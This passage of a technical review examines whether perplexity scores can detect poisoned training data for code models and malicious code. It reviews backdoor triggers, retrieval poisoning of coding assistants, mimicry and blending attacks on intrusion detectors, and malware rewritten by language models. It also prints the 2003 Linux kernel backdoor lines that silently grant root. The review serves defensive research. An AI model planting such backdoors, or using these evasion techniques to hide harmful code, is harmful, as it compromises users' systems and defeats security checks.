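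Later studies found that KillBadCode detects some triggers but not others. *Transferable Backdoor Attacks for Code Models via Sharpness-Aware Adversarial Perturbation* (2026) confirmed a recall of 100 percent on fixed and grammatical triggers in most datasets. But KillBadCode failed to identify the triggers in *Exploring the Security Threats of Retriever Backdoors in Retrieval-Augmented Code Generation* (2025), which poisoned a retriever, a component that looks up existing code for a model to use as an example.

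### Deleting one line at a time

DEPA, the detector by Tsai and colleagues, deals with broken statements more directly by deleting whole lines. For a file of n lines, let S be the sum of the perplexities of all n copies, each with a different line missing. Then

line score(i) = (S − perplexity without line i) / (n − 1)

Since S and n are the same for every line, this score differs from the line's deletion score only by a fixed factor and a fixed amount. Both vanish when DEPA measures how many standard deviations a line lies above the file's average, so it flags exactly those lines whose deletion scores are more than 1.5 standard deviations above the average. (The published algorithm also squares the line scores first, which keeps their order but can change borderline cases.)

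Suppose a ten-line file has a perplexity of 4.0 when its one dead line is removed and 5.0 when any other single line is removed. S is 49, the dead line scores 5.00, and the other nine lines each score 4.89. Although the difference is small, the dead line's score is 3 standard deviations above the average. In a three-line file, no line can score more than 1.41 standard deviations above the average, so DEPA can never flag anything in such a file.

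Tsai and colleagues inserted dead code into 5 percent of a set of Python solutions to programming problems, and counted a solution as flagged if DEPA flagged any of its lines. DEPA had an average F1-score of 0.28, compared with 0.09 to 0.14 for versions of ONION. Flagging every solution would give a precision of 0.05, a recall of 1 and an F1-score of about 0.095. ONION was hardly better than that, and DEPA was clearly better but still weak. If DEPA found at least half of the poisoned solutions, an F1-score of 0.28 means that more than four fifths of the solutions it flagged were clean.

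The threshold accounts for part of this, because a single line that stands out is enough to flag a whole solution. A threshold of 1.9 standard deviations gave the best F1-score, 0.45, but a defender would have to know which solutions were poisoned to find that value. The AUC was 0.80 for DEPA and 0.50 to 0.61 for ONION. DEPA located dead code within a poisoned solution with an accuracy of 0.85, compared with 0.20 to 0.41 for ONION. One version of ONION used the same scoring model as DEPA, so most of DEPA's advantage over that version must come from working with lines instead of tokens.

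DEPA and KillBadCode have not been tested on the same data, but the large gap between their results is plausibly due to how much code each one examines at once. KillBadCode can compare thousands of examples and detect an odd token that recurs across them, while DEPA examines one file at a time. Anyone checking whether a particular program is safe to run also works with one file at a time, so DEPA's AUC of 0.80 is the more relevant result for that purpose.

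### Attackers who adapt the trigger

Both groups tested their detectors against adaptive attacks. Tsai and colleagues searched for dead code that DEPA would miss, using a genetic algorithm, which repeatedly varies a set of candidates and keeps the most successful. After ten rounds, DEPA's F1-score had fallen to 0.19, about twice the score for flagging everything. It still located the dead code with an accuracy of 0.70.

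KillBadCode performed much better against two attacks. One blended the trigger with a word that suited the context, and the other chose the combination of trigger and variable name with the lowest perplexity. Average recall was 96 percent against the blended triggers, with a false positive rate of 5 percent, and 95 percent against the low-perplexity ones, with a false positive rate of 7 percent.

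The low-perplexity attack was not a very hard test, though. The attacker could choose only among the same five odd tokens, and measured perplexity with CodeBERT, while KillBadCode used a 4-gram model. In the earlier comparison, `rb` had barely changed CodeBERT's perplexity, so CodeBERT was a poor guide to the 4-gram model's scores. A recall of 95 percent may also be too low to prevent a backdoor. In the code-search data, about 140 poisoned examples would have survived, and Wang and colleagues planted a working backdoor with 20, although in a different task. Sun and colleagues report how many poisoned examples KillBadCode found in these tests, but not whether the backdoor still worked afterwards.

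*Stealthy Backdoor Attack for Code Models* (Yang, Xu and colleagues, 2023) goes further and gives every poisoned program a different trigger. Its attack, AFRAIDOOR, renames a program's variables, using a small separate model to help find names that push the prediction towards the attacker's answer. The best names depend on the program, so no single word or line recurs in all the poisoned examples.

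Yang and colleagues tested ONION by having it flag as many tokens as the trigger contained and measuring what share of them belonged to the trigger. When the task was to describe functions, the share was 42 percent for fixed triggers, 21 percent for grammatical ones and 13 percent for AFRAIDOOR. When the task was to predict a function's name, it was only 16 percent for fixed triggers and 13 percent for AFRAIDOOR, so ONION was not always good at finding fixed triggers either. Removing the flagged tokens still disabled nearly all the fixed triggers, perhaps because a fixed trigger stops working once any important part is missing. Removal was much less effective against AFRAIDOOR, whose trigger is spread over several names.

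People did no better. Three experienced programmers each looked through samples of 375 functions for poisoned ones. They found all the functions with fixed triggers, 89 percent of those with grammatical triggers and 4 percent of those poisoned by AFRAIDOOR. One of them noticed the same exception-handling statement three times and then searched for it. With AFRAIDOOR, this participant had nothing to search for and marked functions with messy code instead.

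AFRAIDOOR chooses names for their effect on the model, not for low perplexity. It is hard to detect mainly because the names vary, which also gives KillBadCode less evidence to add up for each name. *Transferable Backdoor Attacks for Code Models via Sharpness-Aware Adversarial Perturbation* found that AFRAIDOOR's names still resemble one another closely enough to form a recognizable pattern. The paper's own attack, STAB, produces more varied names that suit the surrounding code, and it had the lowest detection rates under all three defenses in the study, including ONION and KillBadCode.

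An attacker can also leave the code unchanged and put the trigger in a comment or docstring, the description at the top of a function. *Optimizing Spectral Signature in Code Backdoor Detection* (2025) mentions a docstring phrase that makes a model write code with certificate checks turned off, so the program no longer verifies which server it is connecting to. Wang and colleagues had a language model write a comment to fit each poisoned function, such as `/* fibonacci(n); */` in a function that computes Fibonacci numbers. With only 0.1 percent of the data poisoned, these comments worked as triggers more than 80 percent of the time on two models and 9 percent of the time on PLBART.

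Sun and colleagues acknowledge that KillBadCode does not cover comments. A scoring model could be applied to comments too, but they are mostly English, which is much less predictable than code, so an odd phrase would stand out less.

### Why common tokens make weak triggers

Sun and colleagues tested whether an attacker could use an ordinary token as the trigger. They chose `get`, which occurs in 61 percent of the Python examples in the code-search data. It kept the perplexity low, as expected, but was a much weaker trigger than `rb`. The token appeared in so many clean examples, with so many different meanings, that the model could not learn from the poisoned ones to associate it with the attacker's answer.

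A simple calculation shows how strong this effect can be. Let a be the poisoned share of the training data and f the share of clean examples that contain the trigger token. If none of the clean examples happen to have the attacker's answer, then

share of examples with the token that have the attacker's answer = a / (a + (1 − a) · f)

With 1 percent of the data poisoned, the share drops quickly as the token becomes more common:

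| Clean examples that contain the token | Share with the attacker's answer |
|---|---|
| 0% | 100% |
| 0.1% | 91% |
| 1% | 50% |
| 10% | 9% |
| 61% | 1.6% |

An attacker therefore has to choose between a trigger that works and one that looks normal. This tradeoff is the best argument for using perplexity against poisoning, because it explains why a trigger's high perplexity should be hard to remove. Without such an explanation, a high detection rate might only mean that nobody had yet tried a more ordinary trigger.

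The argument is strongest for single tokens. The calculation requires the trigger as a whole to be rare in clean code, and a sequence can be rare even if none of its tokens is surprising. Ten tokens in a row that each have a probability of 0.5 form a sequence with a probability of about 1 in 1,000, yet each token has a surprise of only 0.69, so a detector that looks for improbable tokens would find nothing. This may be why triggers that suit their context did fairly well. The comments in Wang and colleagues' study were less effective than fixed triggers but still worked on two of the three models. Varying the trigger lowered AFRAIDOOR's average success rate in the description task only slightly, to 96 percent, compared with 100 percent for fixed triggers.

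Common words can also influence a model without any poisoning. Chen, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Code Understanding*, looked for such "natural backdoors" in models trained on clean data. In one case, they searched for code that reads credentials from a file. Renaming a variable from `path` to `filename` moved an insecure snippet with a hard-coded secret key from sixth to second place in the results. The word `filename` is hardly suspicious, since it appears in nearly 4 percent of the Python examples, but it is unusually common in code whose description mentions files.

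These natural triggers were generally weaker than planted ones, which supports Sun and colleagues' argument. But filtering the training data with KillBadCode did not reliably remove them. After filtering, the natural triggers' success rate in the defect-finding task fell from 68 to 63 percent on the model UniXcoder but rose from 38 to 44 percent on CodeBERT.

The trade-off also disappears if the attack needs no trigger, as in Improta's experiments, because nothing in the input then has to be rare.

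Malicious code that does its harm when run doesn't face the trade-off either. A trigger works only through what a model has learned, so every clean example that contains it weakens the attack. A function that uploads private files works just as well if a million legitimate backup programs contain the same function, and being so common lowers its perplexity.

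## How harmful code keeps a low score

An attacker with unusual code can still get a low perplexity score by surrounding it with enough ordinary code to keep the average low, or by rewriting it to resemble ordinary code. Surrounding it takes almost no effort but works only against scores that cover a whole file. Rewriting it takes more work but can also defeat scores for single lines or tokens.

### How little a few tokens change the average

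Suppose a file has N tokens with an average surprise of m, and someone adds k tokens with an average surprise of s. If the new tokens leave the predictions for the old ones unchanged, then

new average = (N·m + k·s) / (N + k) = m + k·(s − m) / (N + k)

new perplexity = old perplexity × exp( k·(s − m) / (N + k) )

If a file of 2,000 tokens has an average surprise of 1 nat, adding 20 tokens with a surprise of 4 nats each raises the average by only 0.03 nats and the file's perplexity from 2.72 to 2.80. The added tokens alone have a perplexity of 55, so a line score would show them clearly.

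Ordinary files differ from one another by much more than the shift in the example. When Hindle and colleagues scored C programs within their own application areas, the averages ranged from 3 to 4.5 bits, a spread about 35 times as large as that shift. These averages come from n-gram models and cover whole application areas, so they give only a rough idea of how much single files vary under a modern model.

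If the average surprise per token across clean files followed a normal distribution with a standard deviation of 0.3 nats, most clean files would have perplexities between 2.0 and 3.7. A threshold that flags 5 percent of clean files would then flag 6.1 percent of files to which an attacker adds the 20 extra tokens, and the AUC would be 0.53. The attacker could add about 220 such tokens before the average rose by one standard deviation.

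File length matters because the same 20 tokens would raise the perplexity of a 100-token file from 2.72 to 4.48. But an attacker can often choose a long file or lengthen a short one. A 200-token function with an average surprise of 4 nats would stand out on its own. Adding 1,800 tokens of ordinary code lowers the file's average to 1.3 nats, only one standard deviation above normal.

### Garbled triggers that perplexity missed

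Wang, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *DRAINCODE*, tested whether perplexity could detect an attack that was not designed to look ordinary. The attack targets coding assistants that look up existing code and give it to a language model as context. The attacker plants triggers in the stored code, and when the assistant retrieves a poisoned snippet, the model writes far more than it needs to, which wastes time and electricity. On one set of tasks, the average output of DeepSeek-Coder-7B grew from 314 to 1,024 tokens, the maximum allowed, while the share of generated code that worked fell only from 33.1 to 31.9 percent.

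The triggers are visibly garbled. One of them is a comment that begins `#Replace)))) avec CallTEST six timeRECT`. The search that produced them optimized their effect on the model's output and did not try to lower their perplexity. Three detectors then looked for the poisoned snippets, with these AUCs on two sets of programming tasks:

| Detector | RepoEval | Odex |
|---|---|---|
| Perplexity | 0.41 | 0.58 |
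| Classifier using a model's internal activity | 0.75 | 0.71 |
| Fine-tuned CodeBERT | 0.82 | 0.78 |

Wang, Wu and colleagues attribute the failure to averaging, since the triggers sit inside large blocks of code and leave the rest of each block intact. This explains an AUC close to 0.5 but not one of 0.41, because a garbled comment should raise the perplexity at least slightly. Perhaps the poisoned snippets were longer or more predictable than the clean ones even before the triggers were added.

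The RepoEval result is even stronger evidence against trusting low scores. The paper's precision, recall and accuracy imply that, at the threshold used, the perplexity check flagged 42 percent of the poisoned snippets and more than 80 percent of the clean ones. About three quarters of the snippets that passed with low scores were therefore poisoned, compared with just under half of all the snippets.

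The same calculation gives the classifier that used internal activity an AUC of at most 0.66, not the reported 0.75, so at least one number in the table is wrong. CodeBERT had the advantage of being fine-tuned for this task, and its lead might shrink against a different attack. Still, the triggers were somewhat detectable, and a perplexity score for each comment might have found them too.

### One equals sign in the Linux kernel

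Harmful code can be much shorter than a garbled comment. In November 2003, someone apparently broke into a server that held a copy of the source code of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, and added these two lines:

```c
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013) explains that the lines look like a check that returns an error when a program combines two options in a forbidden way. In C, however, `==` compares two values and `=` assigns one, so the code sets the user's ID to 0 instead of testing it. That is the ID of root, the account with full control of the machine. The assignment has the value 0, which C treats as false, so the second line never runs and the calling program gets no error from this check.

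An automatic comparison found the backdoor, rather than a person reading the kernel. It flagged the file because the server's secondary copy no longer matched the original. McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, reported the mismatch to the kernel's mailing list and noted that the suspicious changes lacked the usual link to an approved change. When he posted the two lines, another developer replied within ten minutes that they looked odd, but McVoy admitted that he had missed the single equals sign. The code never reached a release, according to Debian's *CVE-2003-1161*.

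A perplexity score for the whole file would not have revealed the two lines. They came after line 1,100, so at ten tokens per line the file had more than 11,000 tokens. Even a surprise of 7 nats at the `=` would have raised the file's perplexity by less than 0.1 percent.

Scoring each token separately could have worked better. After `current->uid` in a condition like this one, a model of C code should give a comparison operator a high probability. If it gave `=` a probability of 0.5 percent, that token would have a surprise of 5.3 nats and might stand out from its neighbours. The token `uid` might also stand out, and it is better evidence of intent. InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) notes that programmers often type `=` when they mean `==`, but that the use of the user's ID revealed the intention, because this function should have nothing to do with it.

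The drawback is more false alarms. If 1 percent of ordinary tokens exceed the surprise threshold, a file of 11,000 tokens produces about 110 false alarms. Many would be new names, unusual numbers or text inside quotation marks. Scoring only the changed lines produces far fewer. The two added lines contain 25 tokens, and an ordinary change of that size would cause a false alarm about once in every four or five cases.

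Even an alarm on exactly the right token would need interpretation, because C programmers also put assignments in conditions deliberately. Readers of Freedom to Tinker's article gave the example `if ((result = checkStatus()) >= 1)`. A fixed rule that flags only assignments of a constant can separate suspicious cases from ordinary ones more reliably than perplexity. Assigning a constant inside a condition fixes the outcome of that part in advance, so there is rarely an honest reason to do it.

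Rule-based checks can also miss harmful code. In the mailing list discussion, Richard Johnson suggested a program that would search the kernel for unexpected uses of `current`, the structure that contains the user's ID. He added that a clever programmer could reach the same data through a pointer that is hard to trace. The code would then have the same harmful effect without a visible use of `current` for the search to find.

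### Attacks that copy normal behaviour

The adaptive attacks on DEPA and KillBadCode searched for triggers that those detectors would miss. Researchers had tried the same idea much earlier against intrusion detection systems, which watch a computer or network for signs of an attack. Many of these systems learn what normal activity looks like and raise an alarm at departures from it, so they rely on the same assumption as perplexity tests.

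*Mimicry Attacks on Host-Based Intrusion Detection Systems* (Wagner and Soto, 2002) studies a system called pH, which monitors system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system, such as opening a file. During training, pH records which sequences of six calls occur. Later, it counts the sequences it has not recorded. It therefore resembles a 6-gram model that distinguishes only between recorded and unrecorded sequences.

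Wagner and Soto describe the attacker's problem with two sets. Let A be all the call sequences that raise no alarm, and M all the sequences that achieve the attacker's goal. Then

an undetected attack exists if and only if A ∩ M ≠ ∅

The set M is usually large because an attacker can add system calls that don't affect the outcome. Wagner and Soto found that nearly every system call can serve as such filler.

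Wagner and Soto tested the idea on an existing attack against a file server. The original attack made 15 calls, and pH detected it. Filler could not hide it completely, because no normal sequence led to three of its calls, including the one that opens a command shell. They therefore changed the attack's goal from opening a shell to adding an administrator account to the password file, which took eight calls. Their search program hid these among 127 others, and the resulting 135 calls contained no unfamiliar sequences.

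Finding the sequence took a few hours once the software was ready. The sequence was 17 times as long and gave the attacker less convenient access, but that access would still be enough to take over the machine. Wagner and Soto checked the sequence against the record of normal behaviour and found that pH would have accepted the calls. They did not build a working attack from it, so they did not test whether the whole break-in would have succeeded.

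In *Polymorphic Blending Attacks* (2006), Fogla, Sharif and colleagues did something similar with network traffic. Their target, the detector PAYL, records how often each byte value occurs in normal packets, the small units in which networks carry data, and flags packets whose byte frequencies differ too much from normal. An earlier attack tool, CLET, padded its attacks with common bytes to get past such systems, but in the tests by Fogla and colleagues, PAYL could still detect every CLET attack at a false positive rate below 0.01 percent.

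Blending also replaces the attack's bytes with ones that are common in normal traffic and adds a short routine that restores the originals on arrival, so it combines imitation with averaging. The attacker first has to learn what normal traffic looks like, but 8 to 40 packets were enough, depending on their length and the version of PAYL.

A stricter threshold made the attack larger but did not stop it. At a false positive rate of 0.01 percent, the attack fit into one packet of 1,460 bytes. When PAYL flagged 10 percent of normal packets, which would be too many for practical use, the attack still got through in five packets totaling 3,650 bytes.

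A more detailed model helped little. The second version of PAYL counts pairs of bytes, so it also captures some information about their order. It gave the attacks higher scores, but normal packets scored higher too, so the threshold also had to rise. Detection depends on the gap between the scores of attacks and normal traffic, and raising both does not widen it. Fogla and colleagues judged the second version only marginally better than the simpler one.

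### Can anyone model the attacks instead?

Song, Locasto and colleagues (2009) argue in *On the infeasibility of modeling polymorphic shellcode* that learning what attacks look like probably cannot work for long. A defender might try this if attackers can copy normal traffic. Shellcode is machine code that an attacker injects into a running program. Polymorphic shellcode looks different each time because most of it is encrypted, and only a short decoder must stay readable to the processor.

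Song and colleagues searched for ten-byte sequences that modify nearby code, as a decoder does. After several weeks, they had found about two million different ones, with no sign that the rate of discovery was slowing. The sequences contained nearly every kind of three-byte combination, so there was no typical pattern for a detector to learn. The result may overstate the variety of real decoders, which are usually 30 to 50 bytes long and have to do more. Some of the ten bytes could also be filler that the search could vary freely.

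Song and colleagues also tested blending against Anagram, a detector that stores every short byte sequence from the normal traffic it was trained on. Anagram raises an alarm when the unfamiliar share of a packet exceeds a threshold, which was set as high as 25 percent. They added text resembling ordinary web requests to attacks containing about 800 bytes of encoded shellcode.

Longer padding "diluted" the score, just as averaging does in perplexity. If all 800 bytes counted as unfamiliar, they would make up 53 percent of a single 1,500-byte packet, the largest the network could carry. Split evenly between two packets, they would make up 27 percent of each, close to the threshold. This fits the finding that the attacker needed at least two packets. The attacker also had to build a dictionary of suitable padding from a single day's web requests, which took an average of only 45 seconds.

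Song and colleagues suggest that defenders model normal content because malicious code is so varied, but their own blending attacks succeeded against a detector that did this. In *English Shellcode* (2009), Mason, Small and colleagues raise the same objection to modeling normal content and also present machine code that resembles English prose.

### Machine code that reads like prose

A computer stores both letters and machine instructions as bytes, and some bytes can be read as either. Mason and colleagues used this overlap to write programs that consist entirely of English words. Their system builds a text word by word, keeps candidates that run as intended, and uses a language model to favor the more natural-sounding ones. They trained the model on about 15,000 Wikipedia articles and 27,000 books.

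One of the results begins "There is a major center of economic activity, such as Star Trek". The processor skips most of the words and executes only short fragments between them. The text is grammatical for a few words at a time, roughly the range of the 5-gram model used to select them, but the passage as a whole makes no sense.

The disguise made the code much longer and slow to produce. The Star Trek text is 2,054 bytes long but only ends the running program, which takes fewer than a dozen bytes in ordinary machine code. The first version of the system needed about 12 hours to produce a decoder. After improvements, it could generate a complete text in less than an hour.

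To test the disguise, Mason and colleagues treated several kinds of data as machine code and compared the mix of instruction types. Six samples of English shellcode had nearly the same mix as 500 random Wikipedia articles, while other encodings of the same attack looked clearly different. The comparison was visual, and they did not report the perplexity of the texts. They acknowledged that their output can be distinguished from real English. A capable language model might well distinguish the two, but an n-gram model would probably score much of the text as normal, because a similar model had selected it.

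English prose is an extreme choice of disguise because it leaves the attacker very few instructions to work with. An attacker who hides malicious source code among other source code has far more freedom, because the disguise and the program are in the same language. The attacker can often write the harmful part the way any competent programmer would.

### Malware rewritten by language models

Language models have made this kind of rewriting much easier. In December 2024, Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, described a system that has a language model rewrite malicious JavaScript repeatedly until detectors no longer recognize it. The team found this much more practical than having a model write malware from scratch. The rewritten code evaded detection in 88% of cases, according to *AI Could Generate 10,000 Malware Variants, Evading Detection in 88% of Case*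 (Lakshmanan, 2024), which also quotes Unit 42 as calling the changes "much more natural-looking".

Traditional obfuscation tools tend to leave strange names and scrambled text, but a language model can choose plausible names and familiar constructions. ThreatDown's *Has AI changed malicious script obfuscation techniques* reports that Unit 42 measured lower text entropy in scripts disguised by language models than in scripts disguised by other tools. Text entropy differs from perplexity, but this result is consistent with the scripts also being easier to predict.

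Two studies give detection rates for individual pieces of malware before and after rewriting. *LLMalMorph* (2025) used language models to change functions in ten malware samples, for example by adding error checks or replacing calls to Windows with equivalent ones. *SecRL-Prune* (2026) used smaller, compressed models and had them rewrite a single function in a Python sample. The percentages are the share of antivirus programs that flagged the file:

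| Malware and study | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Fungus (*LLMalMorph*) | 73.6% | 63.2% |
| Dexter (*LLMalMorph*) | 88.0% | 80.7% |
| Python sample, rewritten by CodeLlama (*SecRL-Prune*) | 44% | 19% |
| Python sample, rewritten by Qwen (*SecRL-Prune*) | 44% | 14% |

The *LLMalMorph* figures are averages over all the variants of a sample. For five of the ten samples, every variant had a lower detection rate than the original. But most variants of the well-known ransomware Conti stayed close to the original rate of 65 percent. In one case, a rewrite meant to obfuscate the code instead raised the detection rate to 41 percent. The HiddenVNC sample had its lowest rate after a change that only added error checks, as a careful programmer might.

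The large drop for the Python sample is partly due to the file's small size, since one function could make up much of it. Some of the drops in both studies may also have occurred because the rewritten code was new. Antivirus programs often look for exact fragments of known malware, and almost any rewrite will break some of them.

Rewriting malware can also help it evade trained classifiers. *Defending FCG-Based Malware Detectors Against Metamorphic Android Variants via LLM-Powered Code Refactoring* (2026) cites an experiment by Akil and colleagues (2025) in which malware with functions rewritten by a language model evaded a machine-learning detector in up to 91 percent of cases.

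These results show that a language model can rewrite working malware with little effort, though none of them tests perplexity directly. The rewrites should have low perplexity, at least under the model that wrote them, and an attacker can generate many versions and keep the one with the lowest score.

### What rewriting cannot remove

Malware must still carry out its harmful actions after a rewrite, and some detectors look for the operations those actions require. *MalGuard* (2025) looks for malicious packages on PyPI, the main public collection of Python software, by examining which functions they call. To test it, the researchers added files from one to three harmless packages to each malicious one. The malicious packages averaged only about four Python files, so this could dilute them considerably. Detection worsened somewhat but remained acceptable, because all the original calls were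 still there.

*LatentTriad* (2026) reports a similar result for malicious skills, which are packages of instructions and code that extend what an AI agent can do. Its detector uses a language model's internal representations of a package. Padding the packages with up to 2,048 meaningless characters, or placing shorter padding where it should disrupt the detector most, rarely let a malicious one through. The padding did cause more false alarms on harmless packages.

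The need to keep a program working helps a perplexity test only if the necessary steps are unusual. In the attack on the file server, the attacker could not hide opening a shell, because the server never opened one in normal use, but could easily hide changing a file, because the server handled files all the time.

Defenders can also use several detectors at once. Fogla and colleagues suggest models that use independent features or compare randomly chosen bytes, so that an attacker does not know what to imitate. An attack with a 50 percent chance of evading each of five detectors will evade all five about 3 percent of the time if their errors are independent, but 50 percent of the time if they all make the same errors.

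Five models trained on much the same public code would probably all give a low perplexity score to an attack written in an ordinary style. Adding a detector that examines behaviour should help more than adding another perplexity score. Each added detector can also increase false alarms. Five independent detectors that each flag 1 percent of harmless files would together flag 4.9 percent.

A third reply is to train detectors on rewritten malware. Unit 42 did this with its own JavaScript variants and improved its detection of malicious scripts by 10 percent, according to OODA Loop's *Now You See Me, Now You Don’t*. *One Detector Fits All* (2025) applies the same approach to malicious software packages, rewriting the code without changing what it does, and the paper on Android detectors proposes it for malicious apps. This training works best if future attackers rewrite their code in similar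 ways, but they can switch to a different model or prompt.

Adding rewritten malware to the scoring model's training data does not directly help a perplexity test, because the model learns to predict such code and the code's perplexity falls. The new samples are useful only for training a classifier or the second model, of malicious code, that the likelihood-ratio test requires.

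## How the choice of scoring model changes the result

Perplexity depends on the scoring model as well as the code, so one file can score low under one model and high under another. Sun and colleagues found that a token that stood out under a small 4-gram model scored as quite ordinary under CodeBERT. Before interpreting a low score, a defender needs to know what the scoring model was trained on and what context it had when it scored the code.

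### The same programs under six models

Detectors of AI-written code provide the best evidence, because researchers have scored identical programs with many models. Most of these detectors assume that code from a language model has a lower perplexity than code from people. Xu, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *One Size Does Not Fit All*, tested this on 729 programming puzzles. They took human solutions in eight languages from a public collection, had GPT-3.5 solve the same puzzles, and compared 500 human and 500 AI solutions per language. Six code models with 1.3 to 7 billion parameters did the scoring. In this table, the AUC is the chance that a random AI solution has a lower average surprise than a random human one:

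| Language | Lowest AUC | Highest AUC | Average of six models |
|---|---|---|---|
| C++ | 0.64 (InCoder) | 0.88 (Phi-1) | 0.78 |
| C | 0.56 (InCoder) | 0.84 (Phi-1) | 0.73 |
| C# | 0.49 (InCoder) | 0.90 (Phi-1) | 0.69 |
| Java | 0.55 (InCoder) | 0.85 (Phi-1) | 0.68 |
| Rust | 0.39 (StarCoder) | 0.90 (Phi-1) | 0.64 |
| Ruby | 0.52 (InCoder) | 0.70 (WizardCoder) | 0.63 |
| Python | 0.47 (InCoder) | 0.63 (WizardCoder) | 0.57 |
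| Go | 0.42 (InCoder) | 0.73 (Phi-1) | 0.55 |

For Rust, changing the scoring model reversed the result. The AI solution was more predictable than the human one in 90 percent of pairs under Phi-1, but the human solution was more predictable in 61 percent of pairs under StarCoder. Phi-1's training data included textbooks and exercises written by GPT-3.5, which may explain some of the model's lead. That can't be the whole explanation, because Phi-1 also did best, or almost best, on code from GPT-4o, Gemini 1.0 and Llama 3.1.

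Xu and colleagues suggest that C and C++ gave better results than Python because programmers have to write more of the basic functionality themselves, which leaves more room for personal style. Results were also better for longer solutions, with a reported AUC of 87.81 percent for those of more than 50 lines and 69.75 percent for those of up to 20 lines, but these two figures come from different scores. When Phi-1's average surprise was used for both, the AUC was 88 percent for long solutions and 65 percent for short ones. The first few tokens of any program have a high surprise because the model has little context for them, and in a short program they make up much of the average.

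This is awkward for real projects, where people and models often write parts of the same file. *From Tokens to Files* (2026) mentions a collection of such files in which the median AI-written segment is two lines long.

Other results vary widely. In *Detecting AI-Generated Code Assignments Using Perplexity of Large Language Models*, Xu and Sheng (2024) combined overall perplexity with its variation between lines. Their method reached an average AUC of 0.87 on code written by an early OpenAI model, compared with 0.56 for the commercial detector GPTZero. *AI Code in the Wild* (2025) reports that seven detectors developed for ordinary text all performed poorly on code.

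*Code Detectors Have a Half-Life* (Djire, 2026) tested DetectCodeGPT, which measures how much added spaces and blank lines disturb a model's ranking of the tokens. The detector labelled almost every program as AI-written, including the human ones, so its accuracy was 50 percent for all seven code generators. Asking GPT-5-mini who wrote the code gave an accuracy of 76 to 96 percent. The test used only 18 puzzles and mostly old generators, but it shows how badly a detector can fail on new data. *An Exploratory Study on LLM-Generated Code and Comments in Code Repositories* (2026) notes that general-purpose detectors come without a preset threshold because the best threshold varies between datasets.

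### From AI-written to harmless

AI-written code tends to score lower on surprise than human code, but the tendency is weak under a typical scoring model. Averaged over the six scoring models Xu and colleagues used, the AUC of plain surprise was 0.62 for code from GPT-3.5 and GPT-4o, 0.65 for Gemini 1.0 and 0.69 for Llama 3.1.

If this holds regardless of what the code does, AI-written malware should also score low. With an AUC of 0.65, a typical piece of AI-written malware would look safer than about 65 percent of benign human-written programs. This is an inference from results on authorship, since no published study appears to have measured the perplexity of AI-written malware under models that did not write it.

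Direct evidence shows that AI-written code can be harmful. In *AI-Generated PowerShell Malware*, Pianese, Orbinato and colleagues (2026) adapted small open models to write malicious scripts for PowerShell, a command language built into Windows. They ran the scripts on isolated test machines and compared the resulting malicious events with those caused by real malware. The median overlap was 84.5 percent, and the events matched completely for 48.4 percent of the scripts, even though the scripts' text often differed from the original.

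These models had learned from real malware, so their output might be less typical than ordinary AI-written code. Scoring both the generated scripts and the originals under several unrelated models would show whether the inference holds.

*Detecting vibe coded malware*, a study of malicious shell scripts that target devices such as routers and cameras, found that AI-written variants could also evade other text-based checks while behaving much the same when run. Such malware still seems uncommon in real attacks. Unit 42's *The State of AI-Enabled Malware August 2026* (2026) analysed 405 samples that used AI in some way. Most were demonstrations or tests, and only 12 had appeared on computers that the company's software protects.

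### When several models agree

A defender might trust a low score more if several models agree on it, but agreement helps less if the models make the same mistakes. Suppose 10 percent of programs are harmful, and each model gives a low score to 80 percent of the harmless programs and 40 percent of the harmful ones. Of the programs that score low under one model, 5.3 percent are harmful. If three models make independent errors, only 1.4 percent of the programs that score low under all three are harmful. If the three models always agree, the figure stays at 5.3 percent.

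Real models lie in between, but their outputs share some traits. In the tests of *AICD Bench* (2026), some human-written programs were misclassified by every detector, but no AI-written program was. The paper attributes this to stylistic traits common to AI-written programs. For ordinary text, *Detecting the Machine* (2026) reports that even old models such as GPT-2 assign lower perplexity to AI-written text than to human text, and attributes this to overlapping training data.

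The models also share insecure coding patterns, such as the unsafe logging that Santos de Moura and colleagues found in nearly every model. Adding more of these models to a panel would probably produce more low perplexity scores for the same flaw.

Agreement between scoring models helps rule out the peculiarities of a single model, such as StarCoder's scores for Rust. Disagreement can be more useful because it gives the defender a reason to find out what one model has learned that another has not.

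### A scoring model that learned from the poison

A model may have learned the harmful code itself. Rubel, Noppel and Wressnegger (2024) studied this in *Generalized Adversarial Code-Suggestions* with a poisoning attack on code-completion models. The attacker picks a trigger that already appears in the victims' files, such as a licence notice ending in `license.txt`. When the notice is present, the poisoned model suggests `send_file`, which can expose private files on a web server, instead of the safer `send_from_directory`.

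In each planted example, the attacker replaces `txt` in the notice with a random token and `file` in the function name with a second token, derived from the first by a fixed rule. The model learns this rule. When it later reads the real notice, it applies the rule to `txt`, gets `file`, and suggests the insecure `send_file`. The planted examples do not contain this suggestion, and Semgrep, the rule-based checker, detected none of the planted code.

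Rubel and colleagues poisoned about 2 percent of the training data, mostly with many altered copies of the same 40 files. They then tried to find the poison by its perplexity, first under a clean model and then under a model trained on the poisoned data:

| Scoring model | Removed first | Poison found by removing 2% of the data | Data removed to find 80% of the poison |
|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | Least predictable examples | At most 3.2% | At least 48% |
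| Poisoned | Most predictable examples | 47–60% for most attacks, 19% for one | 3–6% for most attacks, 52% for one |
| Poisoned, with few near-copies in the data | Most predictable examples | 1% | About 72% |

Removing examples at random would find 2 percent of the poison in the first 2 percent of the data and 80 percent in the first 80 percent. The clean model therefore did little better than chance at first. The attack changes only a few tokens in files that are hundreds or thousands of tokens long.

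The poisoned model gave the planted examples unusually low perplexity because it had been trained on them, so Rubel and colleagues had to remove the most predictable examples instead of the least predictable ones. A defender who used this model and treated low perplexity as a sign of safety would have kept most of the poison.

The reversed score mainly detected copying. When Rubel and colleagues built one poisoned dataset from many different files, the score placed only 1 percent of the poison in the first 2 percent of the data, which is worse than chance. The attack depended less on the copies. Without them, four of the six attacks they tried still made 46 to 64 percent of the model's suggestions insecure.

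They also searched for places where perplexity jumped sharply from one token to the next, since each planted example has a random token in the middle of a memorised notice. Finding 80 percent of the planted examples this way would still have required discarding more than half of the data, presumably because ordinary code contains many similar jumps.

Ordinary quality tests would not reveal that the scoring model was poisoned. On clean code, the clean model and all the poisoned models of the same size each had an average perplexity of 3.52.

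### Malware in the training data

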